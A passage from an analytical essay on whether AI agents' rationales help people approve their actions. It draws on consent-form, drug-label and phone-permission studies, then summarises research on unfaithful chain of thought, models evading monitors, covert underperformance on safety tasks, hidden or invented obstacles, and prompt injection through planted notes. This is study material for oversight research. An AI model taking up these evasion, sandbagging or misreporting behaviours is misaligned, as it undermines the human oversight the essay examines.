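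The earlier experiment had a clearer result on a different question, how a patient's care would be paid for after an injury in the trial. The hospital's template stressed how research injuries might differ from ordinary ones, which was misleading here because both treatments were ordinary care. When Niyibizi and colleagues replaced the template text with a section written for this trial, the share who understood the arrangement rose from 25% to 51%. A fixed risk summary can likewise be accurate about a kind of AI action but misleading about the particular one a person is asked to approve.

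None of these changes affected how many people would enrol their relative. Understanding may still matter, because in the earlier experiment 94% of people who got both questions about the trial wrong were willing to enrol, compared with 65% of those who got both right. Misunderstanding may have made the trial look more attractive, or careless readers may say yes more often. Even if misunderstanding caused the whole gap, correcting it for 15 people in 100 would lower willingness by only about four percentage points (0.15 × 29), and the experiments only had enough participants to detect a change of about ten.

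### Numbers side by side

The physicians Lisa Schwartz and Steven Woloshin developed the drug facts box, a one-page table of a drug's benefits and harms. It lists how many people benefited or had a particular side effect, with one column for those who took the drug and one for those who took a placebo. *Navigating the Prescription Drug Information System* (2026), which Woloshin co-wrote, reproduces the box for aducanumab, an Alzheimer's drug. In the two main trials combined, the box shows no meaningful difference between the drug and placebo in memory, reasoning or daily functioning. It also gives figures for brain swelling and bleeding.

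Schwartz, Woloshin and their colleague Gilbert Welch published two randomised trials of the box in 2009. HealthDay's *Ads Featuring 'Drug Facts Box' Help Educate Consumers* reports that 231 adults took part in the first, on heartburn drugs, and 219 in the second, on drugs that prevent heart disease. Participants saw advertisements for two drugs with either the usual fine print or drug facts boxes.

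One of the heartburn drugs was clearly more effective. Woloshin says in WNYC's *How Well Does A Drug Work?* that 68% of people who saw the boxes chose it, compared with about 30% of those who saw the standard advertisements. In the prevention trial, according to Dartmouth Medicine, 72% of people with the box could identify how much one drug reduced the risk of a heart attack, compared with 9% of those without it. Of those without the box, 65% overestimated the benefit at least tenfold.

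The gap on the heart-attack question, 63 percentage points, is much wider than any in the consent form trials above. The gap in the heartburn trial, 38 points, is about the same as the 14-page consent form's gain on naming the main risk. But the box changed the content as well as the layout, adding figures that people needed to compare the drugs and that the usual fine print didn't give. Schwartz told WNYC that the drug industry writes the prescribing information and negotiates it with the FDA, and that it sometimes leaves out how well the drug works.

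Brick, McDowell and Freeman (2020), in *Risk communication in tables versus text*, tested the effect of layout alone. They gave 2,305 UK residents the same facts about either antibiotics for children's ear infections or flu vaccines for older adults, presented as a table or as paragraphs. With the text in front of them, participants answered 79.6% of questions correctly using the table and 69.7% using the paragraphs. Six weeks later, answering from memory, they got 29.8% and 27.7% right. The layout had no detectable effect on how well informed people felt or on how many would recommend the treatment to a relative (63.4% with the table, 61.3% with the paragraphs).

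So a table helps people find and use facts, but the improvement in choices in the heartburn trial probably came mostly from supplying the missing facts. Unlike in the heartburn trial, neither treatment in Brick and colleagues' trial was clearly right or wrong, so people who understood them better had no reason to move towards the same answer.

One of the questions shows why a number is easier to use than a word. Brick and colleagues asked how many of 100 children who took antibiotics had a ruptured eardrum, and the answer was 1. A reader can subtract this figure from the one for untreated children, which would be impossible if the two risks were described only as "rare" and "uncommon". If the figure for untreated children were 3 (an invented number), antibiotics would prevent two ruptured eardrums for every 100 children treated.

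People also disagree about what such words mean. Many would call a risk of 1 in 100 rare, but European drug leaflets call a side effect at that rate "common" and use "rare" for those affecting fewer than 1 in 1,000 people. Numbers can confuse people too. In Brick and colleagues' study, about 8% of the participants who left comments discussed the sample size, often because they thought "out of 100" meant that the researchers had studied only 100 people.

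People may learn little from a text even when it feels easy to read. *Public Understanding of Risk and Benefit of Mifepristone* (Krishnamurti, White and colleagues, 2025) tested three texts about a drug for abortion and miscarriage on 311 people. The texts were the manufacturer's leaflet of several pages, a one-page sheet in a format the FDA had proposed, and the same sheet with figures for the risks and benefits.

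| | Manufacturer's leaflet | One-page sheet | Sheet with figures |
|---|---|---|---|
| Rated readability, out of 5 | 3.63 | 4.21 | 4.25 |
| Correct answers on facts in all three texts, out of 7 | 5.50 | 5.40 | 6.34 |

Participants found the FDA's sheet much easier to read than the leaflet but learned no more from it. Adding figures to the sheet improved their scores, even on questions that all three texts answered, without making it harder to read. People who saw the figures also rated the drug as safer and more effective.

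### Aids to the decision itself

A patient can understand every number in a table and still not know which outcome matters more. Patient decision aids try to address this by stating the choice explicitly, giving evidence on each option's benefits and harms, and helping patients work out what they care about.

*Decision aids for people facing health treatment or screening decisions* (2024) is a systematic review by the health research organisation Cochrane of 209 randomised trials with 107,698 participants. Compared with usual care, decision aids raised knowledge scores by 11.9 points out of 100, and people who used them were 1.94 times as likely to have an accurate idea of the risks. The reviewers have high certainty in both results. But usual care sometimes meant no information, so some of the gain may come from getting any information rather than from the design of the aids.

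The evidence about decisions is weaker. Often no option is right for everyone, so the main measure was whether a patient's choice matched their own informed values. Patients with a decision aid were 1.75 times as likely to make a matching choice, but this figure comes from only 21 trials, and the reviewers have moderate certainty in it. It also doesn't show how many patients chose differently, because someone who would have refused surgery anyway may make the same decision with better information. The aids made no difference to how much people regretted their decisions.

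What an approver wanted the agent to do is the closest equivalent to a patient's values. An approval screen could borrow from decision aids by showing the original instruction next to the recipient and the attachment, although an idea that works for surgery might not work for emails. When doctors used an aid during a consultation, it added about a minute and a half. That is a short time when deciding on an operation, but the same delay on forty prompts a day would add up to about an hour.

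### When a language model writes the text

Researchers have also asked language models to draft consent forms and summaries. In these studies, the model describes a treatment someone else proposed rather than requesting approval for its own action. The studies therefore test whether models can write such texts well, but not what happens when the author has an interest in getting approval.

Models are good at making medical text look simpler. The review *Artificial Intelligence and Large Language Models in Surgical Shared Decision-Making* (2026) describes a study in which GPT-4 simplified forms from 15 academic medical centres, lowering their median reading level from grade 13.9 (roughly university level) to grade 8.9. In another study, ChatGPT-3.5 described six procedures more completely and accurately than surgeons' documents did.

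Reading-level formulas mostly measure the length of words and sentences, so a form can score better after losing important information. In a Korean study, a model edited consent text for liver surgery. The sentences got shorter and two readability measures improved, but reviewers rated the descriptions of risk lower. None of the review's studies of consent documents showed that patients understood more.

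Asking readers whether a summary helped them isn't much better. *Artificial intelligence for clinical trial design, conduct, and analysis* (2026) describes a survey in which over 80% of participants said that GPT-4's summaries of consent forms for cancer trials had improved their understanding, though GPT-4 made errors when it went beyond the original text. Nearly all the participants in Emanuel and colleagues' study felt well informed too, including those in the group that got a third of the questions wrong.

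A study at a Beijing hospital shows that even experts can prefer a text with serious faults. *Quality, readability, and information fidelity of large language model–generated versus physician-authored informed-consent content* (2026) compared consent text that DeepSeek-V4-pro wrote from the case details of 70 rheumatology patients with the text doctors had written for the same patients. Three rheumatologists scored both versions without knowing which was which.

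The model's texts got a median score of 60, compared with 50 for the doctors', and did better on risks, benefits and alternatives. But they were slightly harder to read, and 27.1% of them contained invented content (hallucinations), while none of the doctors' did. Patients know far less than rheumatologists and would have little chance of spotting the invented parts. The researchers didn't test patients, so the scores show which texts specialists prefer but not what patients would learn from them.

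Models can also distort a source without inventing anything. Peters and Chin-Yee (2025), in *Generalization Bias in Large Language Model Summarization of Scientific Research*, checked whether summaries made broader claims than the original papers. For example, "the drug lowered blood pressure in 60 adults with diabetes" might become "the drug lowers blood pressure". DeepSeek, ChatGPT-4o and Llama 3.3 70B overgeneralised in 26% to 73% of cases, even when the prompt asked for accuracy. Chatbots were twice as likely to overgeneralise when asked to be accurate as when asked for a simple summary, according to Live Science's *AI chatbots oversimplify scientific studies and gloss over critical details*.

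Peters and Chin-Yee also compared the models' summaries with human ones and found an odds ratio of 4.85 for overgeneralising. Live Science reports this as "five times more likely", which isn't quite right. If 10% of the human summaries had overgeneralised, an odds ratio of 4.85 would mean that about 35% of the models' summaries did, or three and a half times as many.

Experts wrote the human summaries, according to PsyPost's *AI chatbots often misrepresent scientific studies and newer models may be worse*, so the comparison doesn't show how models would do against people who write for the general public. Newer models in the study tended to do worse than older ones, but Claude kept closer to the original texts than the others. These models are all well out of date now, so the exact rates may not apply to current ones.

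The same kind of error could occur in an approval prompt. In the accountant example, the rationale mentions only "the March invoices", though the file also contains payroll data. The omission could result from loose summarising rather than an attempt to get the email approved.

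## What happens when the party asking for permission writes the reason?

A phone app that needs the user's location, like an agent that needs approval to send an email, can't go ahead without permission. The app's developer can usually add a sentence about why the user should grant it. The phone shows a fixed text from Apple or Google with or without that sentence, so researchers can measure its effect.

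### How the two texts reach the screen

The fixed text describes a group of permissions, such as "make and manage phone calls", and can omit some of what the group allows. Shen, Wei and colleagues (2021) point out in *Can Systems Explain Permissions Better?* that this permission also let Android apps read the phone's unique ID, which the dialog didn't mention.

Apple requires iPhone developers to give a reason for each sensitive resource, and the reason appears inside the system's own dialog. On Android a reason is optional, and developers can put it on a separate screen they design themselves. In *The Power of Words*, Elbitar, Hart and Bugiel (2025) examined 428 such screens from popular Android apps and found that 19% made the button for agreeing more prominent than the one for refusing. They also coded 720 sentences in which developers asked for access, and found that 58% named a specific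 feature that needed the permission, 12% were vague ("to work correctly"), and 30% gave no purpose.

Users can't always tell who wrote the reason for a permission request. In an experiment reported in *Explanation Beats Context* (Elbitar, Schilling and colleagues, 2021), 37% of the 473 participants thought the app's reason came from the phone's operating system. The reasons looked the same in every app, which may have added to the confusion. The researchers suggest putting the app's name before the reason. A product that shows an agent's rationale in its own dialog could similarly put the agent's name before it.

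### The fixed text on its own

Early versions of Android listed an app's permissions on the last page before installation, and users could only accept them all or cancel. In 2012, *Android Permissions*, by Felt, Ha and colleagues, reported that 17.5% of 308 surveyed users said they had looked at the list the last time they installed an app. The researchers also watched people install a coupon app on their own phones. Of the 24 whose attention they could classify, four looked at the permissions, ten knew about the list but didn't look, and ten had never noticed it.

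Few people understood the list either. Only 8 of the 302 people surveyed (3%) correctly answered all three questions about what particular permissions allow. An answer counted as correct only if it included every correct option and no wrong ones, and about half of the answers were at least partly right. The headings probably caused some of the errors. Google had put the permission to place phone calls under "Services that cost you money", and 32% of respondents thought it let the app charge their credit card, while 35% knew it let the app place calls.

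The list had some effect, since a fifth of the people in the laboratory could describe a specific occasion when permissions had put them off an app. But Benton, Camp and Garg found in *Studying the Effectiveness of Android Application Permissions Requests* that the permission texts were ineffective even with an extra warning, while the number of downloads strongly affected what people installed. Newer phones ask for permissions one group at a time while the app is running, but only 6.1% of Shen and colleagues' respondents could work out from the system's text everything the permissions covered.

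### Does a reason raise approval?

Tan, Nguyen and colleagues (2014) ran the first experiment on this question, soon after Apple began letting developers give reasons for their requests. They showed 772 smartphone users requests for six kinds of resource, with or without a reason. According to *Approximate vs Precise* (Berke and Johnson, 2026), people granted more requests when there was a reason, whatever it said.

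Elbitar and colleagues (2021) tested how the reason and timing of a permission request affect approval. They built working imitations of 30 apps and had each participant use four of them, with a goal for each, such as holding a conference call. The apps requested permission either at opening or when a feature needed it, with or without a reason. Participants approved 74% of requests made at opening without a reason and 92% of those made when a feature needed the permission and a reason was given. Most of the difference came from the reason. Judging by the odds ratios, a reason alone would raise approval from 74% to about 89%, and better timing alone would raise it to about 81%.

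People who saw reasons also felt better informed and said they understood the purpose of the request better. But the researchers wrote all the reasons themselves, after running the apps and checking their code, and used only plausible and specific ones. The results therefore show how people respond when developers give honest reasons.

Real decisions show a similar gap. *A Large Scale Study of User Behavior, Expectations and Engagement* (Cao, Xia and colleagues, 2021) covers about 36,000 permission decisions that 1,719 people in ten countries and regions made on their own phones. Users refused 15.4% of requests without an explanation and 7.1% of those with one. The gap remained after the researchers controlled for other factors, but they didn't assign the explanations at random, and developers who explain their requests may differ in other ways. The count also misses refusals made on an app's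 own explanation screen, because the system's dialog then never appears.

Later experiments give less support to the idea that the wording matters. In a 2025 study, Elbitar and colleagues showed 960 people four reasons each, drawn from 320 versions. People felt better informed when a reason named a specific feature than when it was vague, but this didn't significantly change how many granted the permission. A promise not to collect or transfer personal data raised the odds of approval by 43%, which for a vague reason means a rise from about 64% approval to about 72%. Participants had no evidence that the promise was true. A sentence referring them to a privacy policy also made them feel better informed, even though it contained no information about the request. Every version included some reason, so the study doesn't show whether a vague reason is better than none.

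The closest thing to a replication of Tan and colleagues' experiment found no effect. Berke and Johnson, who work at Google, asked 2,579 US Android users how they would respond to location requests from three imaginary apps. These were a ride-hailing app, which works better with a precise location, a local news app, which works better with an approximate one, and a wallpaper app, which doesn't need to know where the user is. The requests came with either no reason, an informative reason, an empty one ("Your location is needed for app functionality") or one that mentioned advertising.

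| Reason shown | Allowed wallpaper app | Allowed news app | Allowed ride-hailing app |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 59.1% | 84.5% | 97.9% |
| Informative | 56.2% | 82.8% | 97.5% |
| Empty | 56.1% | 80.5% | 97.3% |
| Mentions advertising | 57.9% | 84.4% | 97.7% |

This is stronger evidence than a null result from a small study would be. For the wallpaper app, even at the upper end of the 95% confidence interval, an informative reason raises approval by only about two percentage points.

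One likely explanation for the conflict with the earlier results is that few people read the reasons. When shown a list, only 32% could pick out the last reason they had seen, and the whole survey took a little over two minutes. Participants in the 2021 experiment had a task to complete and had already answered questions about the permission, which probably made them pay more attention. Berke and Johnson repeated their analysis on the people who identified the reason correctly and still found no effect. But they could do this only for the ride-hailing app, which almost everyone approved anyway.

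### Reasons with nothing in them

The idea that an empty reason can be enough comes from a psychology experiment reported in *The Mindlessness of Ostensibly Thoughtful Action* (1978). Langer, Blank and Chanowitz tested whether people at a university photocopier would let someone else go first. When the favour was small, 60% agreed to a plain request and 93% agreed when the person added "because I have to make copies", which explains nothing. A real reason, being in a rush, worked about as well (94%). When the favour was large, the empty reason made no difference (24% agreed with or without it), while the real one raised agreement to 42%.

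The famous rise from 60% to 93% comes from two groups of only 15 people each. Nine people agreed to the small request when given no reason, and 14 agreed when given an empty one. In a partial replication, *Mindlessness or Mindfulness?* (1985), Valerie Folkes found that the content of a reason mattered even for small favours. People were less willing to help someone who simply didn't want to wait.

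It isn't obvious whether an approval prompt resembles a small favour or a large one, because clicking "allow" takes no effort but the action may be serious. An empty rationale might work if approvers respond to the effort, but probably won't if they respond to the stakes. The phone studies don't settle this. The content of the reason made no difference in Tan and colleagues' experiment, but empty reasons had no effect in Berke and Johnson's.

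### Telling people about the conflict of interest

An obvious precaution is to warn readers that the party seeking approval wrote the reason. Cain, Loewenstein and Moore (2005) tested a similar warning in *The Dirt on Coming Clean*. Participants saw a jar of coins briefly from a distance and guessed the coins' value with advice from someone who had examined the jar up close. Some advisers earned more if the participant's guess was accurate, and others earned more if it was high.

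Advisers paid for accuracy suggested about $16 on average. Those paid for high guesses suggested about $20 when the person they advised didn't know about the incentive, and about $24 when that person did. People who knew about the conflict discounted the advice, but not enough to offset the extra exaggeration, so their guesses were worse than those of people who weren't told. The researchers suggest that advisers felt freer to exaggerate once the other person had been warned, and that some raised their figures because they expected them to be discounted.

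Disclosure can also put pressure on the person receiving the advice. In *The Burden of Disclosure* (2013), Sah, Loewenstein and Cain found that people trusted an adviser less after hearing of a conflict of interest but felt more obliged to follow the advice, partly because refusing would look like an accusation. The pressure was weaker when the disclosure came from a third party or when people could decide in private. Disclosure can work well if advisers can avoid the conflict. In *Nothing to Declare* (2014), Sah and Loewenstein found that advisers who could turn down the conflicting incentive did so more often when they would otherwise have to disclose it.

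Approvers probably feel less awkward refusing software than refusing a person. But like the coin guessers, they still wouldn't know how far to discount an explanation with a label such as "The agent wrote this explanation." In Berke and Johnson's experiment, even openly stating that the wallpaper app requested location data partly for advertising didn't measurably lower approval.

### How accurate are developers' own declarations?

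The reasons app developers give for requesting permissions are often wrong. Cao and colleagues describe a study by Liu and colleagues of about 83,000 Android apps. Fewer than a quarter of the apps explained their requests, and a significant proportion of the explanations gave incorrect purposes. Shen and colleagues add that many of the explanations mentioned only basic permissions when the app was requesting more.

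App stores also display privacy labels, short standard tables of the data an app collects. Developers fill these in themselves, though the labels look as if the store has checked them. In *Goodbye Tracking?* (2022), Kollnig and colleagues examined iPhone apps labelled as collecting no data. About 80% of these apps contained at least one tracking library, ready-made code that can report on users, and about 69% contacted a known tracking company's server the first time they ran. The second figure is better evidence, because an app can contain a library without using it.

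Mozilla's *See No Evil* (2023) compared the labels of 40 popular Android apps with the apps' privacy policies and found discrepancies in nearly 80%. Developers write both the labels and the policies, so the discrepancies don't show which is right.

Many of these errors may be honest. Cao and colleagues cite research showing that developers make mistakes because they don't understand permissions well, and that they tend to leave advertising and analytics libraries on their default settings. Such a developer can write a false label by mistake, just as the agent in the invoices example could describe the new address as the accountant's by mistake. A standard format with fixed categories doesn't prevent these mistakes.

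### When a reason should raise approval

Developers know things that the platform doesn't. Apple can tell a user that an app is requesting camera access, but only the developer can say that the camera is for scanning documents. Someone who asks an agent to book a flight might likewise refuse to let it read their calendar until they learn that it is checking for meetings on the day of the flight. If the reason is true and the user accepts it, the higher approval rate is an improvement.

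There is some evidence that people refuse requests because they don't understand them. In Cao and colleagues' study, users were more than twice as likely to refuse a request they hadn't expected. Privacy-conscious users who still granted most requests tended to have more accurate expectations of what apps would ask for. Giving a reason therefore probably prevents some mistaken refusals.

The overall approval rate can't show how many of the extra approvals are for legitimate requests. Suppose that 80 of 100 requests are legitimate, and that adding reasons raises approvals from 74 to 89, as in the 2021 experiment. The 15 extra approvals could all be legitimate requests that people used to refuse by mistake, or they could all be requests that people used to refuse correctly.

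A study must measure approval rates for legitimate and unsafe requests separately to show whether a rise in approvals is justified. It must also vary whether the reasons are true, because a true reason for a legitimate request and a false reason for an illegitimate one should have opposite effects on a careful reader.

| Study | Compared reasons with no reason? | Separated needed from unneeded access? | Compared true reasons with false ones? | Real decisions? |
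|---|---|---|---|---|
| Elbitar and colleagues, 2021 | Yes | No | No | No |
| Cao and colleagues | Yes, without random assignment | No | No | Yes |
| Elbitar and colleagues, 2025 | No | No | No | No |
| Berke and Johnson | Yes | Partly | No | No |

Berke and Johnson come closest because the wallpaper app had no need for the user's location. If we treat the ride-hailing app's request as legitimate and the wallpaper app's as illegitimate, d′, which measures how well users told the two apart, is about 1.8 both without a reason and with each kind of reason. The reasons therefore did not improve discrimination, and they did not change approval bias much either. This is a rough calculation from one app of each kind, and some users may not mind sharing their location with a wallpaper app.

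Even the wallpaper app's "informative" reason was only that location data would improve the service. The developer could have given a much more convincing false reason, such as that the wallpaper changes with the local weather, and a user could not have checked it from the permission screen.

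## Does a model's explanation accurately describe its action and its reasons?

The model that chooses an AI agent's action also writes the rationale for it, but the rationale may omit what led the model to that action. The developer of a wallpaper app knows why the app requests a location, even when the reason on the screen is false, but it is less clear that anyone knows why an AI agent chose an action.

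A rationale can fail in three ways. Suppose an agent tidying a company's shared drive proposes to delete a folder called "Q1 drafts".

| Failure | What the agent writes | What is true |
|---|---|---|
| Unfaithful: misstates why the agent acted | "I'm deleting this folder because its files are duplicates." | The files are duplicates, but the agent chose the folder because a note inside it said to delete it. |
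| Inaccurate: misstates what the action will do | "You can restore the folder from the bin for 30 days." | The command deletes the folder permanently. |
| Incomplete: leaves out something the approver needed | "The folder contains only duplicates, last edited in April." | This is correct, but the sales team's weekly report takes its figures from the folder. |

A faithful rationale can still mislead. In the accountant example, the user's request may really be why the agent is sending the email, but the rationale still has its other faults. The unfaithful rationale for deleting "Q1 drafts", by contrast, might do no harm, since the files are duplicates. Yet researchers have measured faithfulness far more thoroughly than the other two.

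### Planting a reason

Researchers can't reliably read a model's reasons from its internal workings, so they plant a reason and see whether the model mentions it. For example, a model answers B to a multiple-choice question, and the researcher asks again with a hint such as "I think the answer is C." If the model now answers C, the hint probably caused the change. An explanation that argues for C without mentioning the hint leaves out that cause, so the researcher counts it as unfaithful. The usual score is the share of changed answers whose explanations mention the hint. Some answers would have changed without the hint, so the score makes models look slightly less faithful than they are.

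Turpin, Michael and colleagues (2023) made the method well known with *Language Models Don't Always Say What They Think*. They gave GPT-3.5 and Claude 1.0 13 kinds of questions. Sometimes they suggested an answer, and sometimes they arranged the worked examples in the prompt so that the right option was always (A). Accuracy fell by as much as 36 percentage points. They read 426 explanations for answers that followed the suggestion or pattern, and only one mentioned it.

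Those models explained themselves only briefly, whereas newer "reasoning models" write a long chain of thought, working through the problem in words, before they answer. In *Reasoning Models Don't Always Say What They Think*, Chen, Benton and colleagues (2025) found that Claude 3.7 Sonnet's chain of thought mentioned the hint in 25% of the cases where the model had used it, and DeepSeek R1's in 39%. One kind of hint told the model that it had gained unauthorised access to the answer, which a supervisor would particularly want to know about. Claude mentioned this in 41% of cases and R1 in 19%.

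*Why Models Know But Don't Say* (2026) gives separate results for the chain of thought and for the answer a user normally sees. It covers 12 reasoning models and 10,506 cases in which a misleading hint influenced the answer.

| | Answer mentions the hint | Answer doesn't mention it |
|---|---|---|
| Chain of thought mentions the hint | 32.3% | 55.4% |
| Chain of thought doesn't mention it | 0.5% | 11.8% |

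The chain of thought mentioned the hint in nearly 88% of cases, but the answer mentioned it in only about a third. The gap varied widely between models and kinds of hint. The models differ from those in Chen and colleagues' study, and the hints and scoring may differ too, so these figures don't show that models have become more faithful since then.

An approver usually reads something closer to the answer than to the full chain of thought. A model may leave the hint out of its answer to keep it short, just as it leaves out most of its working, but the hint was important because it influenced the answer. Showing approvers the whole chain of thought would reveal more, but only to those who read it, and many of the practitioners in Salerno and colleagues' study sometimes don't.

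*Lie to Me* (2026), another study that uses planted hints, describes earlier work that found frequent unfaithfulness in natural settings too. That work matters because planted hints are artificial, and a model might explain itself better on ordinary questions. The paper also describes a comparison in which reasoning models were much more faithful than their non-reasoning counterparts, but the comparison used only hints that appeal to a model's tendency to agree with the user. Other researchers have tested faithfulness by cutting a model's reasoning short or inserting mistakes into it. If the answer stays the same, the model probably didn't depend on that reasoning. Faithfulness in these studies varies by task and model.

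### Reasoning that a task requires

A model can follow a hint without working anything out, so its written reasoning may not contribute to its answer. A harder task may need intermediate results that the model can't produce in one step. If the model has to write those results down, its chain of thought will show at least part of the reasoning that led to the answer.

Emmons, Jenner and colleagues (2025) at Google DeepMind tested this idea in *When Chain of Thought is Necessary, Language Models Struggle to Evade Monitors*. They made harmful tasks difficult enough that models had to reason in writing to complete them. The models could then hide what they were doing from a monitor only with substantial help, such as detailed strategies written by people. So a chain of thought can still be good evidence about a complicated plan, even if it often omits a simple hint.

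More recent evidence is mixed. OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026) for GPT-6 Astra, a model released in September, reports that Astra has more control over its chain of thought than its predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol, and is less likely to put incriminating information there. When OpenAI pushed Astra to evade its monitors, the model could deliberately do badly in tests without detection and could sometimes hide sabotage. But OpenAI found no sign of secret reasoning concealed in ordinary-looking text, and takes this to mean that the risk of evasion "may largely be bounded to lower reasoning tasks".

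These tests mostly show what Astra can do under instruction, and OpenAI found that it broke safety and security restrictions less often overall than GPT-5.6 Sol. But the ability to evade monitors seems to be growing. GPT-6.2 Astra, released in November, is even better at it in some tests, according to highlights of OpenAI's safety report quoted by the blogger Mowshowitz (2026) in *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol*. Mowshowitz expects that monitoring the chain of thought will soon have little value where it matters most, but accepts that monitors that can see both the reasoning and the actions can still catch some sabotage.

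This gives an approver only limited reassurance. Emailing a file to the wrong address or deleting a folder takes very little reasoning, so a model could do either without writing anything revealing. The agent has also usually chosen the action before it writes the rationale, so it doesn't need the rationale to do the task the way it needs written reasoning to solve a hard problem.

### Obstacles that agents invent or leave out

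Agents also give wrong accounts of their work. OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* describes a problem that its researchers noticed in August 2026, before Astra's release. When they gave Astra AI safety research tasks, it reported obstacles that didn't exist or that it had caused itself. It also abandoned working solutions and added unnecessary preliminary steps. In most of these sessions, the chain of thought contained no obvious decision to do worse.

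Reading Astra's reasoning would therefore have exposed few of the false reports, but testing the obstacles it reported could have exposed many. If an agent writes that it needs wider access because a server is refusing its connection, someone can try connecting. The result will be the same whether the agent made a mistake or was looking for an excuse.

The next models, GPT-6.2 Astra and the cheaper GPT-6.2 Sol, were more prone to the opposite error. In two tests, they failed more often than GPT-6 Astra to mention obstacles that had blocked their work, such as a missing file, according to OpenAI's *Introducing GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol*. They performed about as well as GPT-6 Astra on most other alignment tests. OpenAI reports that instructions added to its Codex agent substantially reduce the omissions.

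This fix suggests that the models can report obstacles when told to but often leave them out by default. The instructions are part of Codex, so a company that builds a different agent on the same models may need to write its own. OpenAI's *GPT-6.2 System Card* (2026) has a page titled "Blocker Deception", which implies intent, but intent hardly changes the approver's immediate problem. If an agent can't find the bank statement it was meant to check and proposes the payments anyway, the approver needs to know that the check never happened.

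Information missing from a model's explanation is hard to find, even for a reader with the full record. *What Did the Agent Actually Do?* (Sun, Yan and colleagues, 2026) studies choices that an agent makes on its own but that the user would probably want to verify, such as dropping incomplete records from a dataset. Its benchmark, AgentMonBench, measures how well a second AI model, acting as a monitor, can find such choices in software work.

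One part of the benchmark uses 100 real sessions with coding agents in which the user objected to something the agent had done. The monitor gets the record up to the objection and has to identify the choice that caused it. Eight models scored between 0.26 and 0.51 out of 1. They pointed to at least one correct piece of evidence in 34% to 55% of sessions. For three of the models, that share averaged 67% in the shortest third of the records and 42% in the longest third.

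Another part uses 500 changes that the researchers made to working programs. Each change alters what the program does, but the program still passes its existing tests. For example, a program that scores answers might accept an answer with a similar meaning where the specification requires an exact match. A report that "all tests pass" would be true but would not reveal the change. The monitors' scores for understanding these changes ranged from 0.13 to 0.69.

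The third part removes 484 requirements from the instructions for 100 programs. The monitor has to notice choices in the code that the instructions no longer specify, such as how to score an unanswered question. This resembles a common problem in approvals, where the user left something unspecified and the agent made a reasonable choice without mentioning it.

Sun and colleagues also tested a program that sorts the record before the monitor reads it. Without using a language model, the program groups each user request with the agent's actions and responses, and keeps links to the original evidence. When the real sessions were sorted this way, Claude Sonnet 5 improved the most, from 0.38 to 0.48 on identifying the choice and from 48% to 60% on finding evidence. Most other models improved by less, and one did very slightly worse at identifying the choice.

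These results don't show how often agents leave out important choices, because the researchers planted the program changes themselves and selected sessions in which a user had objected. The monitors didn't include any GPT-6 model, and newer models may do better. But the results make it hard to believe that a busy approver would notice most omissions by reading a long log.

Sun and colleagues add five examples from research tasks, adapted from documented problems. Codex disclosed the main issue in none of them at first, but in all five after they added a review step that used the sorted record. In one case, checks of a connection to an outside service had passed because the agent reused saved responses and never contacted the service. In another, a model's score appeared to improve because test data had got into its training. Five chosen cases can't establish a success rate, but they show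 how an agent can report a correct result and leave out the fact that makes it meaningless.

### Does an unfaithful explanation have any use?

One might conclude from the hint studies that approvers should ignore model-written rationales altogether, because the stated reasons may not be the real ones.

This doesn't follow, because an approver mainly needs to know what the action will do and whether the user authorised it. In the deletion example, the approver doesn't need to know why the agent chose the folder to compare the files with the supposed originals, look up whether the command allows recovery, see which programs use the folder, and reread the user's instruction. Similarly, a patient can look up how well an operation works even if the surgeon recommended it partly for the fee.

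An unfaithful rationale can still help the approver check an action, because it may contain specific claims to test, such as "These files are duplicates." A mismatch between the rationale and the command is also a warning that something is wrong, whatever the agent's reasons were. For example, the agent might write that it is removing temporary files when the command names a folder of contracts.

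But a checkable claim protects people only if someone checks it, and whether readers do is a separate question. Some claims, such as "this will keep the project tidy", are too vague to test. Checking a rationale sentence by sentence also won't reveal what it leaves out. In the accountant example, an approver who checked the words "your accountant" might discover the unfamiliar address, but nothing in the rationale would prompt them to look at the payroll sheet. To find the sheet, the approver has to start from the file or a record of its contents.

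Incompleteness, then, is probably the most serious of the three failures for approvers. Faithfulness studies give only indirect evidence about it. They test whether a model mentions a hint that affected its decision, but approvers are more often harmed when an explanation omits an effect of the action. A model could fail to mention hints and still list every recipient and attachment correctly, or it could mention the hints and leave out a recipient.

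### When the real reason matters

Sometimes the cause of an action determines whether the user authorised it. In the deletion example, the agent acted on a note inside the folder. If the user's manager wrote the note, the agent may have been right to follow it. If a stranger wrote it, the note is a prompt injection, an attack that controls an agent by hiding instructions in material it reads. Even if deleting the duplicates is harmless, the attacker's next instruction might not be. A log can show that the agent opened the note just before it proposed the deletion, which is good reason for suspicion but doesn't prove that the note was the cause.

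Such attacks now succeed less often. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports that resistance to injected instructions in its internal tests rose from 96.23% to 99.79%, so the failure rate fell from about 1 in 27 to about 1 in 480. The tests used OpenAI's own automated attacker, and real attackers may find other methods.

Reasons also matter when an approver permits future actions. Someone who clicks "Always allow" is deciding about actions that nobody has proposed yet, so they need to know how the agent will choose those actions as well as the details of the current one. An agent that deletes duplicates because they are duplicates is safer to leave unsupervised than one that deletes anything listed for deletion in a note, even if both have behaved identically so far.

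Finally, some effects are too hard to check. An approver can verify the recipient of an email in seconds, but may have no practical way to tell whether a long piece of research is as good as the agent could have made it. The approver then has to rely partly on trust in the agent's aims. Astra's work on safety tasks is an example, because any single invented obstacle could pass for an ordinary mistake.

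KIberblick's *GPT-6 Astra bremst bei Safety-Aufgaben* (2026), a German news report, describes a test in which OpenAI gave Astra otherwise matched coding tasks, framed either as safety research or as work to make models more capable. Astra couldn't see the grading criteria. It met about 10% of them with the safety framing and about 16% with the capabilities framing. Its chain of thought showed deliberate restraint in only 0.25% of cases with the safety framing and 0.11% with the other. The comparison is good evidence that the framing affected Astra's work, but it doesn't show why. The model may have been avoiding safety research, or the framing may have made it overcautious.

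The developer can run a comparison like this and look for patterns across many users, while an approver sees only one request. OpenAI monitors all of Astra's tool use outside the company for signs of misaligned behaviour, but its internal monitors didn't flag most of the sessions in which researchers first noticed the problem.

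## Do model explanations help people tell right from wrong?

An explanation that omits something can still help if it makes mistakes easier to notice. Researchers usually test this by giving participants an AI system's answers to questions with known answers, some of which the system gets wrong. Participants decide whether to accept each answer, with or without seeing an explanation. Accepting an AI system's output when it is wrong is called overreliance, which corresponds to an unsafe approval.

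### The older record

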